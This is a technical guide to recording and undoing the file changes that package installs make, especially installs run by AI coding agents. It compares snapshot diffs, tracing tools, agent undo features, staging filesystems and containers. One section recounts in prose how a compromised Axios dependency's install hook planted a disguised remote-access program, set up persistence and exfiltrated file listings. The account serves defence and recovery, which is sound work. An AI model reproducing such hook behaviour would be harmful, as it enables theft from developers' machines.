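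In *NaSh*, Gyawali, Kallas and colleagues (2025) propose a command shell that would automatically keep earlier versions of files. Commands would change the real files, and the shell would store the old versions in a separate layer for each command. According to Zhong and colleagues, YoloFS's journal also records what each path held before a change.

The new contents matter because the user may edit a file after the install. If the user has since edited `~/.bashrc`, restoring the old copy would erase that edit. Comparing the file with a checksum taken right after the install would reveal the change. Gyawali and colleagues suggest version numbers for the same purpose. They also describe a conflict that these checks can't catch, in which a later install adds a package that depends on an earlier one. Undoing only the earlier install would break the later package, so the record should at least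 show the order of the installs.

*Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* (Bui, 2026) describes OpenDev, a coding agent with an operation log that tracks file changes for rollback. But if a harness logs only the edits made with its own editing tool, the log won't include files that an install hook writes.

### A before-and-after comparison

The simplest way to record what an install changed is to describe the relevant files before and after it, then compare the two descriptions. This needs only standard tools. The commands below are for Linux.

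1. **Choose the locations.** Start with the project, including its `.git/config` file and anything Git ignores. Add the shell profiles, `~/.npmrc`, `~/.gitconfig`, `~/.config`, `~/.local/bin`, the agent's own configuration and the directory for global packages. For large caches, names and sizes are usually enough.
2. **Hash the files.** The first `find` command below computes a checksum for each file. The second lists each path's type, permissions, owner, group and link target. Run them from a directory outside the chosen locations, so that the lists don't include themselves.

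   ```bash
   places=(~/project ~/.bashrc ~/.profile ~/.npmrc ~/.gitconfig ~/.config ~/.local/bin)
   find "${places[@]}" -type f -exec sha256sum {} + | sort -k 2 > before.sums
   find "${places[@]}" -printf '%p %y %m %u:%g %l\n' | sort > before.meta
   ```

3. **Save the small configuration files.** A checksum can show that a file changed but can't restore it. Copy the shell profiles and settings files into an archive that preserves permissions, and note which files don't exist yet.
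4. **List the global packages.** Save the output of commands such as `npm ls -g --all`, `uv tool list` and `dpkg -l`, because package managers' own records may not keep the old version numbers.
5. **Install.** Write down the exact command, the directory, and the start and end times. With npm, add `--foreground-scripts` so that the hooks' output appears in the log. If the package builds later, as Rust packages do, continue until the first successful build.
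6. **Compare.** Repeat the two `find` commands with new output names and run `diff` on each pair of lists. A path that appears only in the second list is new, and one that appears only in the first is gone. A different checksum means that the contents changed. The second pair of lists also reveals changes to permissions and links.
7. **Attribute.** Match each change to a package and, where possible, to a hook.

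If `~/.bashrc` is a symbolic link, which is common among people who keep their settings in a Git repository, `find` records the link but doesn't hash the file it points to. Adding that file to the list fixes this.

Saved copies of `~/.npmrc` and a project's `.env` file often contain access keys, so the archive should be readable only by its owner and stay out of version control. A malicious hook with the user's permissions could also read the archive or alter the lists. For a suspect package, it is safer to keep both where the install can't reach them.

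The results should also include the list of locations compared, so that a reader can tell whether the comparison found no changes in `~/.config` or didn't cover it. The install-tracking script `pio`, which Linux From Scratch publishes, can display the directories it watched and ignored for a particular package.

Comparing checksums is slower than searching for recently modified files, but more reliable. An installer can give a new file the date stored in its archive, as `tar` does by default, so the file may look years old.

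### Separating the hook from the rest of the install

Comparing two snapshots shows what changed between them, but not whether the package manager or a hook made the changes. A third snapshot often makes this clear.

With npm, you can separate a hook's changes from the rest of the installation by first installing the package with `--ignore-scripts`, which unpacks the files without running any hooks. After approving the package, if npm 12 requires it, you can take a second snapshot, run `npm rebuild` for that package, and take a third. Changes between the first two snapshots come from npm and the approval, while those between the last two come from the hook, unless another program was writing at the same time. When several packages have hooks, rebuilding them one at a time, with a snapshot after each, separates their changes.

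pip allows a similar split. `pip wheel` builds a package from source, and `pip install` can then unpack the finished wheel. Files that appear in the home directory during the first command probably come from the build code or from pip's cache.

This takes longer than an ordinary install, and some packages fail if their hooks run out of order. It is worth the time for a package with a hook that nobody recognizes, but probably not for every routine update.

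### What the comparison misses

A before-and-after comparison can miss a lot, as the March 2026 attack on Axios shows. The malicious hook was in a dependency called `plain-crypto-js`. Datadog Security Labs' *Compromised axios npm package delivers cross-platform RAT* (2026) traces the hook's effects on each operating system.

On a Mac, the hook put a program in `/Library/Caches`, under a name that resembled an Apple service. On Windows, the hook downloaded a program that added a script to the shared `ProgramData` directory and a registry entry to run that script at every login. Checking only the home directory would have missed the Mac program and the Windows script. Comparing files wouldn't directly reveal the registry entry, so Windows users also need to export the relevant registry keys before and after the install.

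Temporary files cause a different problem. The hook deleted its script, `setup.js`, and left a clean `package.json`, so a comparison made afterwards would show a new package folder with no sign of a hook. According to Veracode's *Breaking Down the Axios Supply Chain Attack*, the only remaining clue was that the lockfile listed version 4.2.1 while the clean `package.json` gave 4.2.0. A snapshot taken between unpacking and running the hook would have included `setup.js`, and comparing it with a later snapshot would have shown that the file was deleted.

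On Linux, the hook saved its program as `/tmp/ld.py`. People often leave `/tmp` out of a comparison because so many programs write there. The program then sent the attacker lists of the files in the user's home directory, documents, desktop and configuration folders. According to Datadog Security Labs, this worked even in containers, where a bug made the program crash right afterwards. A comparison would have missed this theft whichever locations it covered, because sending the lists changed no files.

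Other programs also write files during an install. An editor might save a project, a browser might update its settings, or a second agent might install something else. A checksum can show that a file changed, but not which program changed it. Closing other programs and running one install at a time reduces these unrelated changes. Taking two snapshots a few minutes apart, with no install in between, shows which files change anyway.

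The piuparts tests avoid most of this noise because they run in a minimal Debian installation, as described in Debian's *piuparts(1)* (2023). On a laptop in daily use, the same comparison would list many unrelated changes.

A filesystem with built-in snapshots, such as Btrfs or ZFS, can quickly save the state before an installation, including file contents. But Zhong and colleagues note that a snapshot of part of the disk covers only locations chosen in advance and combines changes from every program writing there.

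### Sending the install to an empty directory

Another approach is to give the installer an empty home directory, prefix and cache. Whatever appears there must have come from the install, so there is no need for a first snapshot. For an imaginary npm tool called `deploykit`, the commands could be:

```bash
t=$(mktemp -d)
mkdir "$t/home"
cp -p ~/.bashrc ~/.profile "$t/home/"
HOME="$t/home" npm install -g --prefix "$t/prefix" --cache "$t/cache" \
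  --allow-scripts=deploykit deploykit@2.0.0
find "$t" ! -type d
```

Copying the shell profiles makes the test more realistic, because some installers edit a profile only if it already exists and an empty home directory could hide that change. Comparing the copies with the originals afterwards shows any edits. Unsetting variables such as `XDG_CONFIG_HOME` and `XDG_CACHE_HOME` before the test keeps them from overriding the usual locations under `HOME`.

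This method helps find files that an install puts in unexpected places. If a hook downloads a browser, the files show up in the temporary home directory even if nobody knew which cache the hook used. However, the install may behave differently than it would in the user's real home directory. For example, npm won't find the user's `~/.npmrc`, so it may use another registry or fail to log in to a private one. An upgrade also looks like a new install, because the empty prefix has no older version to replace.

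Redirection works only if the installer follows the settings. Walton (2020), in *Monitor filesystem write to a specific directory?*, describes a package whose `make install` command ignored the library directory Walton had specified. It appeared to use a fixed `lib` directory instead, which broke the installation on Red Hat and Solaris systems. A hook can likewise write to a full path such as `/home/sam/.bashrc`, even if `HOME` has been changed. Redirection is therefore unsuitable for code that might be malicious, unless the whole test runs in a disposable environment.

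A union filesystem is harder to bypass than an empty prefix because it also captures writes to fixed paths. Commands can read the existing files, but their changes go to a separate directory, so the originals remain available for comparison. *ShellVis* (2026) uses this method to show programmers what each command in a shell script does, and empties the separate directory before running the next command. Upgrades are also more realistic than in an empty prefix because the old version of the tool is present.

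*ShellVis* doesn't contain network requests, and it may assign a change to the wrong command if several commands write at once. Gyawali and colleagues add that changes to special files under `/proc` and `/sys`, which control the running system, don't take effect in such a layer. An installer that depends on those changes may fail or behave differently.

### Install recorders

An install recorder monitors an install as it happens. Installwatch is one of the oldest. It needs no preparation phase because it monitors processes while they run (de Mauro, 1998, *Welcome to installwatch 0.7.0beta1*). It places its own code between a program and the system's C library, then logs calls that create, change or delete files.

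Statically linked programs bypass this code because they have the C library built in instead of loading it at run time. This matters more for agents' installs than it did for the C programs of the 1990s, because many tools written in Go are statically linked. If a JavaScript hook starts one of these tools, Installwatch may log the hook's writes but miss the tool's.

CheckInstall builds on Installwatch. It runs `make install`, or another command the user supplies, and turns the resulting files into a Debian, RPM or Slackware package, so the user can remove the software with the system's package manager. By default, it also backs up existing files that the install would overwrite. According to its documentation, it records only files changed by its own processes, while tools that search the disk by date also pick up other users' changes.

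CheckInstall suits a program compiled from source that puts new files under `/usr/local`. It is a poor fit for a two-line edit to `~/.bashrc`, because package managers remove whole files, not individual lines. According to the Debian Wiki, CheckInstall must also run as root for most useful actions, so using it to observe an unfamiliar package would give that package's code more privileges than an ordinary install would.

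*Package Analysis*, a project of the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF), runs new packages from public registries in a sandbox. It records which files they access, which addresses they contact and which commands they run, and publishes the results. It also looks for changes in a package's behavior over time, such as an established library contacting a new server.

*Pack-A-Mal* (Vu, Nguyen and colleagues, 2025) describes an analysis with three phases: installing, importing and executing the package. The import phase could expose import-time code like that in jscrambler 8.18.0, but the default execution time is 10 seconds, so the analysis may miss code that waits longer. The project's code documentation on pkg.go.dev (2025) lists a summary of file writes among the results and describes saving the data the package wrote.

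OpenSSF's sandbox reports cover the file reads and network traffic that a before-and-after comparison misses, but they describe what happened in the sandbox, not on the user's machine. The sandbox doesn't contain the user's shell profile or the older version of a global tool, so the reports can't provide the earlier contents that a change record needs. A hook may also behave differently on another operating system. The reports are most useful before an install, for deciding whether to run the package and which locations to watch.

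Packj can run an install on the user's own machine under strace, a Linux program that logs other programs' requests to the operating system. For its separate package-auditing command, Packj's documentation recommends turning on tracing only in a container or virtual machine, because the package could run malicious code.

### Tracing a change to its hook

Operating-system tracing can connect a changed file to the process that wrote it, and that process to the hook that started it. With strace's `-f` option, for example, a log might show npm starting a shell, the shell running `node install.js`, and that script writing to `~/.bashrc`. The command and its working directory usually identify the package. Newer tools trace inside the Linux kernel and can follow a change after the original process ends. *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) marks files that an agent's processes write and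 passes the mark to programs that later read them, which adds 0.2% to 3.5% to running time. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) also links these events to the language-model exchange that led to them. In one test, it traced a network connection back to an agent's request even though a separate scheduler had started the program later. The three tasks the researchers timed took up to 8% longer, but they haven't measured how often the links are wrong or missing. A shared file can also connect unrelated programs, so a link is evidence of a cause but doesn't prove it. Tracing a write doesn't preserve the file's old contents, so the user still needs a backup.

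### A constructed example

Suppose a user asks an agent to set up browser tests and deployment for a project in `~/shop`. The user, the project and the packages are invented. The machine runs Linux with npm 12, and npm's global prefix is `~/.npm-global`. The project has already approved the hooks of `pagetest` and `git-tidy`. The agent runs two commands in the project directory:

- **Command A, 10:02:** `npm install --save-dev pagetest git-tidy`
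- **Command B, 10:06:** `npm install -g --allow-scripts=deploykit deploykit@2.0.0`

The hook in `pagetest` downloads a browser. The hook in `git-tidy` sets `core.hooksPath`, which tells Git where to find Git hooks, the programs that Git runs at moments such as a commit. These are separate from install hooks. The second command upgrades `deploykit` from 1.4.0 to 2.0.0, and its install hook adds these lines to `~/.bashrc`:

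```bash
export DEPLOYKIT_HOME="$HOME/.deploykit"
source "$HOME/.npm-global/lib/node_modules/deploykit/completion.bash"
```

The full record would look like this:

| Command and cause | Path | Before | After | Permissions or link |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A, npm | `~/shop/package.json` | Saved copy | Two development dependencies added | 644, unchanged |
| A, npm | `~/shop/package-lock.json` | Saved copy | 38 packages added | 644, unchanged |
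| A, npm | `~/shop/node_modules/` | None of the 38 folders existed | 38 new folders, with checksums in a separate list | Permissions and command links in the same list |
| A, `postinstall` of `pagetest` | `~/.cache/pagetest/` | Didn't exist | Browser, 310 MB | Directory 755, browser program 755 |
| A, `postinstall` of `git-tidy` | `~/shop/.git/config` | Saved copy, with no `core.hooksPath` | `core.hooksPath` set to `.githooks` | 644, unchanged |
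| B, npm | `~/.npm-global/lib/node_modules/deploykit/` | Version 1.4.0, with a saved copy of the folder | Version 2.0.0, with checksums in a separate list | Directory 755, unchanged |
| B, npm | `~/.npm-global/bin/deploykit` | Link to 1.4.0's `cli.js` | Link to 2.0.0's `bin/main.js` | Both full link targets saved |
| B, `postinstall` of `deploykit` | `~/.bashrc` | Saved copy, 118 lines | 120 lines, with the two new lines at the end | 644, unchanged |
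| A and B, npm | `~/.npm/` | List of names and sizes | New downloads and logs | Not recorded |

The Git diff would normally show only the changes to `package.json` and `package-lock.json`. Git doesn't track its own settings file, `.git/config`, even though it is inside the project directory.

The saved copy of `deploykit` matters because reinstalling version 1.4.0 could bring in newer versions of its dependencies. If the folder is too large to copy, the output of `npm ls -g --all` at least records the old version numbers.

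The next table shows what each method would catch. It assumes that the Installwatch user has set a backup directory.

| Change | Before-and-after comparison | Empty home, prefix and cache | Installwatch | Package Analysis |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Manifest and lockfile | Yes | No, npm still writes them in the project | Yes | No |
| New folders in `node_modules` | Yes | No, they also stay in the project | Yes | Only in its own sandbox |
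| Browser | Yes, if the list includes `~/.cache` | Yes, if the hook follows `HOME` | Yes, unless a statically linked program writes it | Probably, with the download address |
| Git hooks path | Yes, if the list includes `.git/config` | No | Yes, if Git is dynamically linked | Perhaps the command, but not this project's file |
| Upgrade of `deploykit` | Yes, including the old version | Only version 2.0.0 | New files, and possibly a backup of the old ones | Only the version it tested |
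| Link to the `deploykit` command | Yes, with both targets | Only the new target | The new link, but perhaps not the old target | Only a link in its own sandbox |
| Shell profile | Yes, with both versions | Yes, if the user copied the profile first | Yes, with a backup | Perhaps the new lines, but not the user's file |
| npm's cache | Names and sizes | New files only | Yes | No |

Of the four methods, only the before-and-after comparison can capture the required earlier state for every row, and only if the user chooses the right locations. A user who skips `~/.cache` and `.git` to save time would miss the browser and the Git hooks path. A trial run with an empty home directory can reveal the browser's location, so the user can add it to the list before the real install. The trial would reveal the Git setting only if the user also ran it in a copy of the project.

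The comparison also doesn't show what to enter in the "cause" column. The `deploykit` hook probably added the new lines to `~/.bashrc`, since they mention the tool by name. The cause of the Git setting is less clear, because two packages ran hooks during the same command. Running `npm rebuild git-tidy` on its own in a fresh copy of the project, with a snapshot before and after, would show whether that package's hook changed the setting.

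## Restoring the earlier state or discarding the environment

With a record like the one for `~/shop`, the user can reverse an agent's changes one at a time and keep any later work. This takes effort, so people often prefer to restore a saved state, which returns a whole set of files to how they were at an earlier moment. Restoring also removes later changes unrelated to the install. Replit, a service for building apps in a browser, warns users about this when describing its rollback feature.

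Deleting a disposable environment, such as a container, doesn't require a list of the install's changes and leaves the user's other files alone. But someone has to set up the environment before the install, and the install may still change things outside it.

### Reversing the example row by row

Suppose the user added `alias gs='git status'` to the end of `~/.bashrc` a week after the two installs. Restoring the saved copy would erase the alias, so the user should remove only the two lines that the `deploykit` hook added.

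This order works for the whole record:

| Step | Change | How to reverse it | What to check first |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Two lines in `~/.bashrc` | Delete those two lines | They still match the record |
| 2 | `deploykit` 2.0.0 and the link to it | `npm install -g deploykit@1.4.0` | Nothing written since needs 2.0.0 |
| 3 | Two development dependencies, their lockfile entries and 38 folders | `npm uninstall pagetest git-tidy` | No later test uses them |
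| 4 | `core.hooksPath` in `~/shop/.git/config` | `git config --local --unset core.hooksPath` | The value is still `.githooks` |
| 5 | Browser in `~/.cache/pagetest` | Delete the directory | No other project uses it |
| 6 | Downloads in `~/.npm` | Leave them | Nothing |

For step 1, the user can copy the two lines from the record into a file called `added-lines.txt` and run:

```bash
grep -vxF -f added-lines.txt ~/.bashrc > bashrc.new
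diff ~/.bashrc bashrc.new
cat bashrc.new > ~/.bashrc
```

The `diff` should show only two deleted lines. Using `cat` instead of moving the new file into place keeps the old permissions and any symbolic link.

It is usually best to reverse the newest install first, because it may depend on an earlier one. Within an install, the order depends on how the changes are connected. The profile lines are removed before `deploykit` 2.0.0 because one of them loads a file from the package's folder. If version 1.4.0 lacks that file, leaving the line in place would make every new terminal print an error. The browser is removed after `pagetest`, because any npm command that reran the package's hook could download the browser again.

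Reinstalling `deploykit` 1.4.0 also restores the link to its program. If newer dependencies make the tool misbehave, the user can replace the new folder with the saved copy. npm 12 will skip any install hook in 1.4.0 unless the user allows it again. If somebody ran version 2.0.0, it may have converted its data in `~/.deploykit` to a format that 1.4.0 can't read, and the record doesn't cover that change.

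Restoring the saved `package.json` in step 3 would be quicker, but it would drop any dependency the user added later. `npm uninstall` keeps those entries. Step 4 is easy to forget, and if it is skipped, Git keeps ignoring the user's own hooks in `.git/hooks`, which may include checks that normally run before each commit.

The recorded checksums show when such care is unnecessary. If a file still matches its checksum from just after the install, the user can restore the saved copy. If it matches the checksum from before the install, somebody has already reversed the change.

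Afterwards, the user can repeat the comparison against the original lists. The remaining differences should be the user's own work and npm's cache. Terminals that were already open keep the `DEPLOYKIT_HOME` variable until the user closes them.

### Why agents' undo commands miss installs

Many coding agents have an undo command, but it would reverse little of what these two installs changed and could make the remaining changes harder to find.

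According to Bui, OpenDev has two ways to undo changes. Its operation log saves a file's contents before the agent changes it and keeps up to 50 operations in memory. The log covers only OpenDev's own file tools, so it misses what `npm install` does in the shell. To fill this gap, OpenDev also saves the project's state to a separate Git repository in the user's home directory whenever a step changes files. `/undo` then restores each file that differs from the saved version.

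In `~/shop`, these snapshots would restore `package.json` and `package-lock.json`. They follow the project's `.gitignore` rules, so they would normally leave out `node_modules`. They would also miss `.git/config`, which Git never includes in its snapshots, and the browser, `deploykit` and the shell profile, which are outside the project. The snapshots can therefore reverse changes only to project files that Git doesn't ignore, although Bui writes that they make all filesystem changes reversible. After the undo, the project's Git diff would be empty, but the hidden changes would all remain.

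Claude Code's `/rewind` covers even less of an install. According to Anthropic, it tracks only files that Claude changes with its editing tools, not those changed by shell commands. If the agent did nothing but install packages, the menu doesn't offer to restore code. `/rewind` also skips symbolic links and hard links, including the package files that pnpm links into a project.

A rewind can undo only part of an install's changes if Claude also edited files directly. According to Anthropic's description of file checkpointing for developers, restoring a file can undo a shell command's changes to it if Claude had also changed that file with an editing tool. If Claude edits `package.json` and then runs `npm install`, a rewind could therefore restore `package.json` but leave the new `package-lock.json`.

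Codex may not have an undo command. In April 2026, OpenAI's *Configuration Reference* still included an undo setting, off by default. A month later, *Slash commands in Codex CLI* listed no `/undo`. Over the summer, a user asked for its return in the forum thread */undo and Conversation Pollution in Codex*. Even the earlier undo design normally left ignored files alone, according to the commit message *feat*, so it wouldn't have removed `node_modules`.

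Codex's sandbox can prevent some of these changes. It normally limits writes to the project and blocks network access, so most installs fail there until the user lets them run outside it. The user can instead turn on network access within the sandbox and give npm a cache directory it can write to. Install hooks then can't edit `~/.bashrc`, but they can still send out anything they can read.

Other agents' undo features have similar gaps:

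- **Cursor.** In its 2025 documentation, Cursor describes checkpoints as local snapshots of the agent's changes to the codebase. That excludes global programs and shell profiles. A 2026 bug report, *Incomplete rollback to the checkpoint when working with subagents*, describes a restore that kept the changes made by subagents, the helpers that the main agent starts.
- **Gemini CLI.** Google introduced checkpointing in 2025 as an optional feature. It saves the project in a separate Git repository before the agent's own file tools make a change. An install in the shell doesn't trigger a checkpoint.
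- **Copilot CLI.** According to GitHub, it takes a snapshot of the workspace as soon as the user enters a prompt. This is better suited to installs because the snapshot exists before any shell command runs, but the feature restores the repository, not the rest of the machine.
- **Kiro CLI.** Amazon's agent also uses a separate Git repository. Kiro lists files outside the working directory among the things it doesn't track.

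These features are still useful for what they were mainly built to do, which is to reverse bad edits to source code.

### YoloFS holds changes until the user accepts them

Zhong and colleagues designed YoloFS to cover changes anywhere in the file system, whichever program makes them. If an install hook writes to `~/.bashrc`, YoloFS copies the file to a separate storage area and applies the write to the copy. The agent's later commands read the new version, but the original file stays the same. Zhong and colleagues call this staging.

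After each command, YoloFS takes a snapshot and lists the changed files for the agent. The agent can return to any earlier snapshot, and YoloFS keeps the abandoned state in case going back was a mistake. At the end, the user reviews the combined changes and either commits them to the real files or discards them.

Only the user can commit or discard. This protects the saved state better than a separate Git repository in the home directory, which an agent or an install hook can usually delete.

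In the example, the agent could remove `deploykit` 2.0.0 by restoring the snapshot taken between the two commands. Removing `pagetest` and `git-tidy` while keeping `deploykit` is harder because each snapshot includes all earlier changes. The agent would have to restore the state from before the first command and then rerun the second.

Staging can also conflict with the user's own edits. If the user adds an alias to the real `~/.bashrc` while YoloFS holds the agent's version, committing that version could overwrite the alias. The published design replaces the file with the staged copy and has no step for merging the two.

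When Zhong and colleagues edited and built the Linux kernel, YoloFS was as fast as an ordinary file system, except that committing more than 100,000 files took an extra 3.5 seconds. On 112 simple file tasks, Claude Code succeeded 99% of the time with YoloFS and 98% without it, and needed the user 0.4 times per task instead of 0.9. The main obstacle is that YoloFS runs inside the Linux kernel, so it can't protect a Mac, and it supports only two kernel versions.

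### HerAgent returns to the step that caused the problem

Restoring the state before the last command may not be enough. *HerAgent* (Li, Lu et al., 2026) describes an agent setting up DataHub, which combines Java, Python and Node.js. The agent installed Node 17 without an error, but seven commands later the web interface failed to start because it needed an old hashing method missing from Node 17's version of the OpenSSL library. Undoing only the last command would have left the wrong version of Node in place, while starting again would have discarded working system packages.

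HerAgent sets up projects inside Docker containers. It groups related commands into blocks, such as installing system packages, setting up a language or installing the project's dependencies. It then works through them as follows:

1. It runs a block and checks the result, for example by asking the test program to find the project's tests.
2. If the check passes, it saves the container's file system as an image.
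3. If something fails, it tries a repair in the running container, adds the fix to the block's script, and runs the block again from the previous image.
4. If the logs suggest that an earlier block caused the failure, it restores the image from before that block, repairs the block, and runs the later ones again.
5. At the end, it runs all the scripts in a clean container and accepts the setup only if they work there.

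Li and colleagues tested it on four datasets. The table compares HerAgent with an earlier agent that used the same model, and also gives its results with the newer GPT-5.4:

| Dataset | Projects | Earlier agent | HerAgent, same model | HerAgent, GPT-5.4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ExecutionAgent-Bench | 50, in 14 languages | ExecutionAgent, 66.0% | 70.0% | 80.0% |
| Repo2Run-Bench | 420, in Python | Repo2Run, 86.0% | 87.1% | 94.0% |
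| SetupBench | 54, in several languages | OpenHands, 46.3% | 70.4% | 90.7% |
| Installamatic-Bench | 40, in Python | Installamatic, 52.0% | 85.0% | 92.5% |

With the same model, HerAgent leads by two projects on the first dataset and five on the second. Its lead on SetupBench is larger but harder to interpret, because HerAgent gets credit if any of three attempts succeeds. Its separate rounds succeeded on 48.1%, 63.0% and 64.8% of projects. If OpenHands had only one attempt at each project, its 46.3% is more fairly compared with those figures. The result on Installamatic-Bench is more convincing, since the earlier agent had up to ten attempts.

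HerAgent returned to an earlier block in only 20 cases, 14 of which ended in success. That result is encouraging, but 20 cases are too few to measure the benefit precisely. HerAgent was also slow, averaging 10 to 38 minutes on three of the datasets.

In another test, Li and colleagues stopped HerAgent from writing its repairs into the scripts, and success on SetupBench with GPT-5.4 fell from 90.7% to 25.9%. Two thirds of the setups still passed HerAgent's own checks in the running container, but only 37% did after a rebuild from the scripts. An agent's manual fixes inside a container can therefore also be hidden changes, which the user may discover only after the container is gone.

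### Virtual environments, containers and Nix

A disposable environment removes only what stayed inside it, and the common types keep different things in:

| Environment | What it keeps separate | What can still get out | Does a rebuild give the same result? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Python virtual environment | Python packages and their commands | Build code can write anywhere the user can | Only if the project fixes exact versions, and source builds may still differ |
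| Container | Files and processes | Changes to mounted folders and shared caches, and anything sent over the network | The same image gives the same files, but a new build may not |
| Virtual machine | A whole operating system with its own kernel | Changes to shared folders, and anything sent over the network | A saved image does, but a new setup may not |
| Nix | Each package and its dependencies | Whatever the programs do when someone runs them | Usually very close, if the project fixes its inputs |

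A mounted folder is a folder on the user's computer that a container can also open. People often mount the project to see the agent's edits immediately. If the agent had run both commands in a container with only `~/shop` mounted, deleting the container would have removed the browser, `deploykit` 2.0.0 and the profile lines. The two dependencies and the Git setting would have remained because they are in the project.

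The next time the user made a commit on their own computer, outside the container, the Git setting could then cause Git to run a program that a package had put in `.githooks`. It is safer to clone the project inside the container and bring the work out as Git commits, which don't include `.git/config`. The user should still review any scripts in those commits.

Sharing a package cache between containers saves time, but the cache remains after a container is discarded. The lockfile has no checksums for the prebuilt modules that install hooks save in `~/.npm/_prebuilds`, so a malicious package could leave an altered module there for the next container to use. Giving unfamiliar packages their own cache avoids this but requires another download.

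Secrets in a container also need protection from install hooks. According to OpenAI's *Codex* documentation, the cloud version installs dependencies during a setup phase, when it has access to the network and to secrets such as access keys. Codex removes the secrets before the agent starts work, but an install hook could already have read them.

The package manager Nix keeps each version of a package in its own directory. When someone installs or upgrades a package, Nix creates a new generation, which is a set of links to the chosen versions. `nix profile rollback` switches back to the previous generation. For a tool like `deploykit`, this would restore version 1.4.0 with its original dependencies. Nothing would need to be downloaded unless someone had deleted the old generation to free up space.

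Nix packages don't run install hooks in the user's account, and on Linux, Nix normally builds packages in a sandbox. But a generation doesn't include personal files or databases. If a new version of a program changes the format of its data, switching back to an earlier generation won't restore the old format. Nix also doesn't manage what an agent installs with `npm install -g`, even if Nix supplied npm.

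A rebuild may give a different result because registries keep changing. For example, a Dockerfile (the list of steps for building a container image) that runs `npm install -g deploykit` without a version may produce a different image next month. Li and colleagues say the same problem limits how well their own experiments can be repeated. Someone who wants the old state back should therefore keep the image itself, though updating the setup still requires the Dockerfile. If the Dockerfile uses exact versions and a lockfile, a rebuild should give nearly the same result as the saved image.

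For a small Python project, a virtual environment takes almost no effort to set up and is usually enough. Containers take more work, use disk space, can be slow with mounted folders on a Mac, and often need extra setup for graphical programs or a graphics card. In the forum thread *Creating snapshots of previous states*, a participant describes using clean virtual machines to test install instructions, but wouldn't do this on an everyday computer. It seems sensible to use a container or virtual machine for an unfamiliar repository or a package with an unexplained hook, and just a saved copy of the relevant files for a routine upgrade of a trusted tool.

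### What no restoration reverses

Restoring files can't undo effects on other computers. If a hook has sent an SSH key to an attacker, the user has to revoke the key. To prevent such leaks, YoloFS asks the user before a command reads files in their home directory. A hook could still read secrets in environment variables, because it receives those without opening a file.

A stolen npm token can let an attacker publish new versions of the user's packages. The user can withdraw or deprecate those versions, but other people may already have installed them. Similarly, people may already have read an email, chat message or GitHub comment by the time the user deletes it. Reversing changes to a remote database requires a separate backup of that database. Replit's rollback leaves databases unchanged by default and never restores the production database automatically.

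In these cases, the user can only take a further action, such as revoking a key, publishing a clean release or sending a correction. A change record helps by showing when the install ran and which secrets it could read.

### After a suspected malicious install

Reversing the listed changes isn't enough if the package may have been malicious, because its code could have altered the record, the saved copies or the tools used to check them. It could also have written to places that the comparison didn't cover. The jscrambler program, for example, set itself to start again at login, so removing the package left it running.

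The user should therefore replace the credentials and rebuild the machine in an order that doesn't expose the new credentials:

1. Disconnect the affected machine from the network. If an investigation is likely, keep a copy of the disk and the agent's logs.
2. From another device, revoke every credential that the install could have read. That may include SSH keys, cloud and npm tokens, browser passwords, login sessions and keys for AI services. Check that the old ones no longer work, because both Cline and Jscrambler initially revoked the wrong token.
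3. Reinstall the operating system, or start from an image made before the suspect install. A later snapshot may contain the same malicious program.
4. Bring back documents and reviewed source code. Leave behind `node_modules`, virtual environments and caches, and check shell profiles and Git settings before copying them.
5. Remove the bad version from the lockfile before reinstalling anything. Otherwise, an exact rebuild will install it again.
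6. Look for unfamiliar package releases, logins and messages in the affected accounts.

A full rebuild can take a day or more, so the response should depend on what the code could reach. If the package ran in a container with no credentials and no mounted folders, deleting the container is probably enough. If npm 12 skipped the hook and nobody ran or imported the package, its code may never have started. Cline's unwanted hook did run, but it contained a single readable command that installed a known program, OpenClaw, so uninstalling that program was a reasonable response. A hook that downloaded and started an unknown program on a developer's everyday computer justifies a full rebuild, even if a later scan finds nothing.
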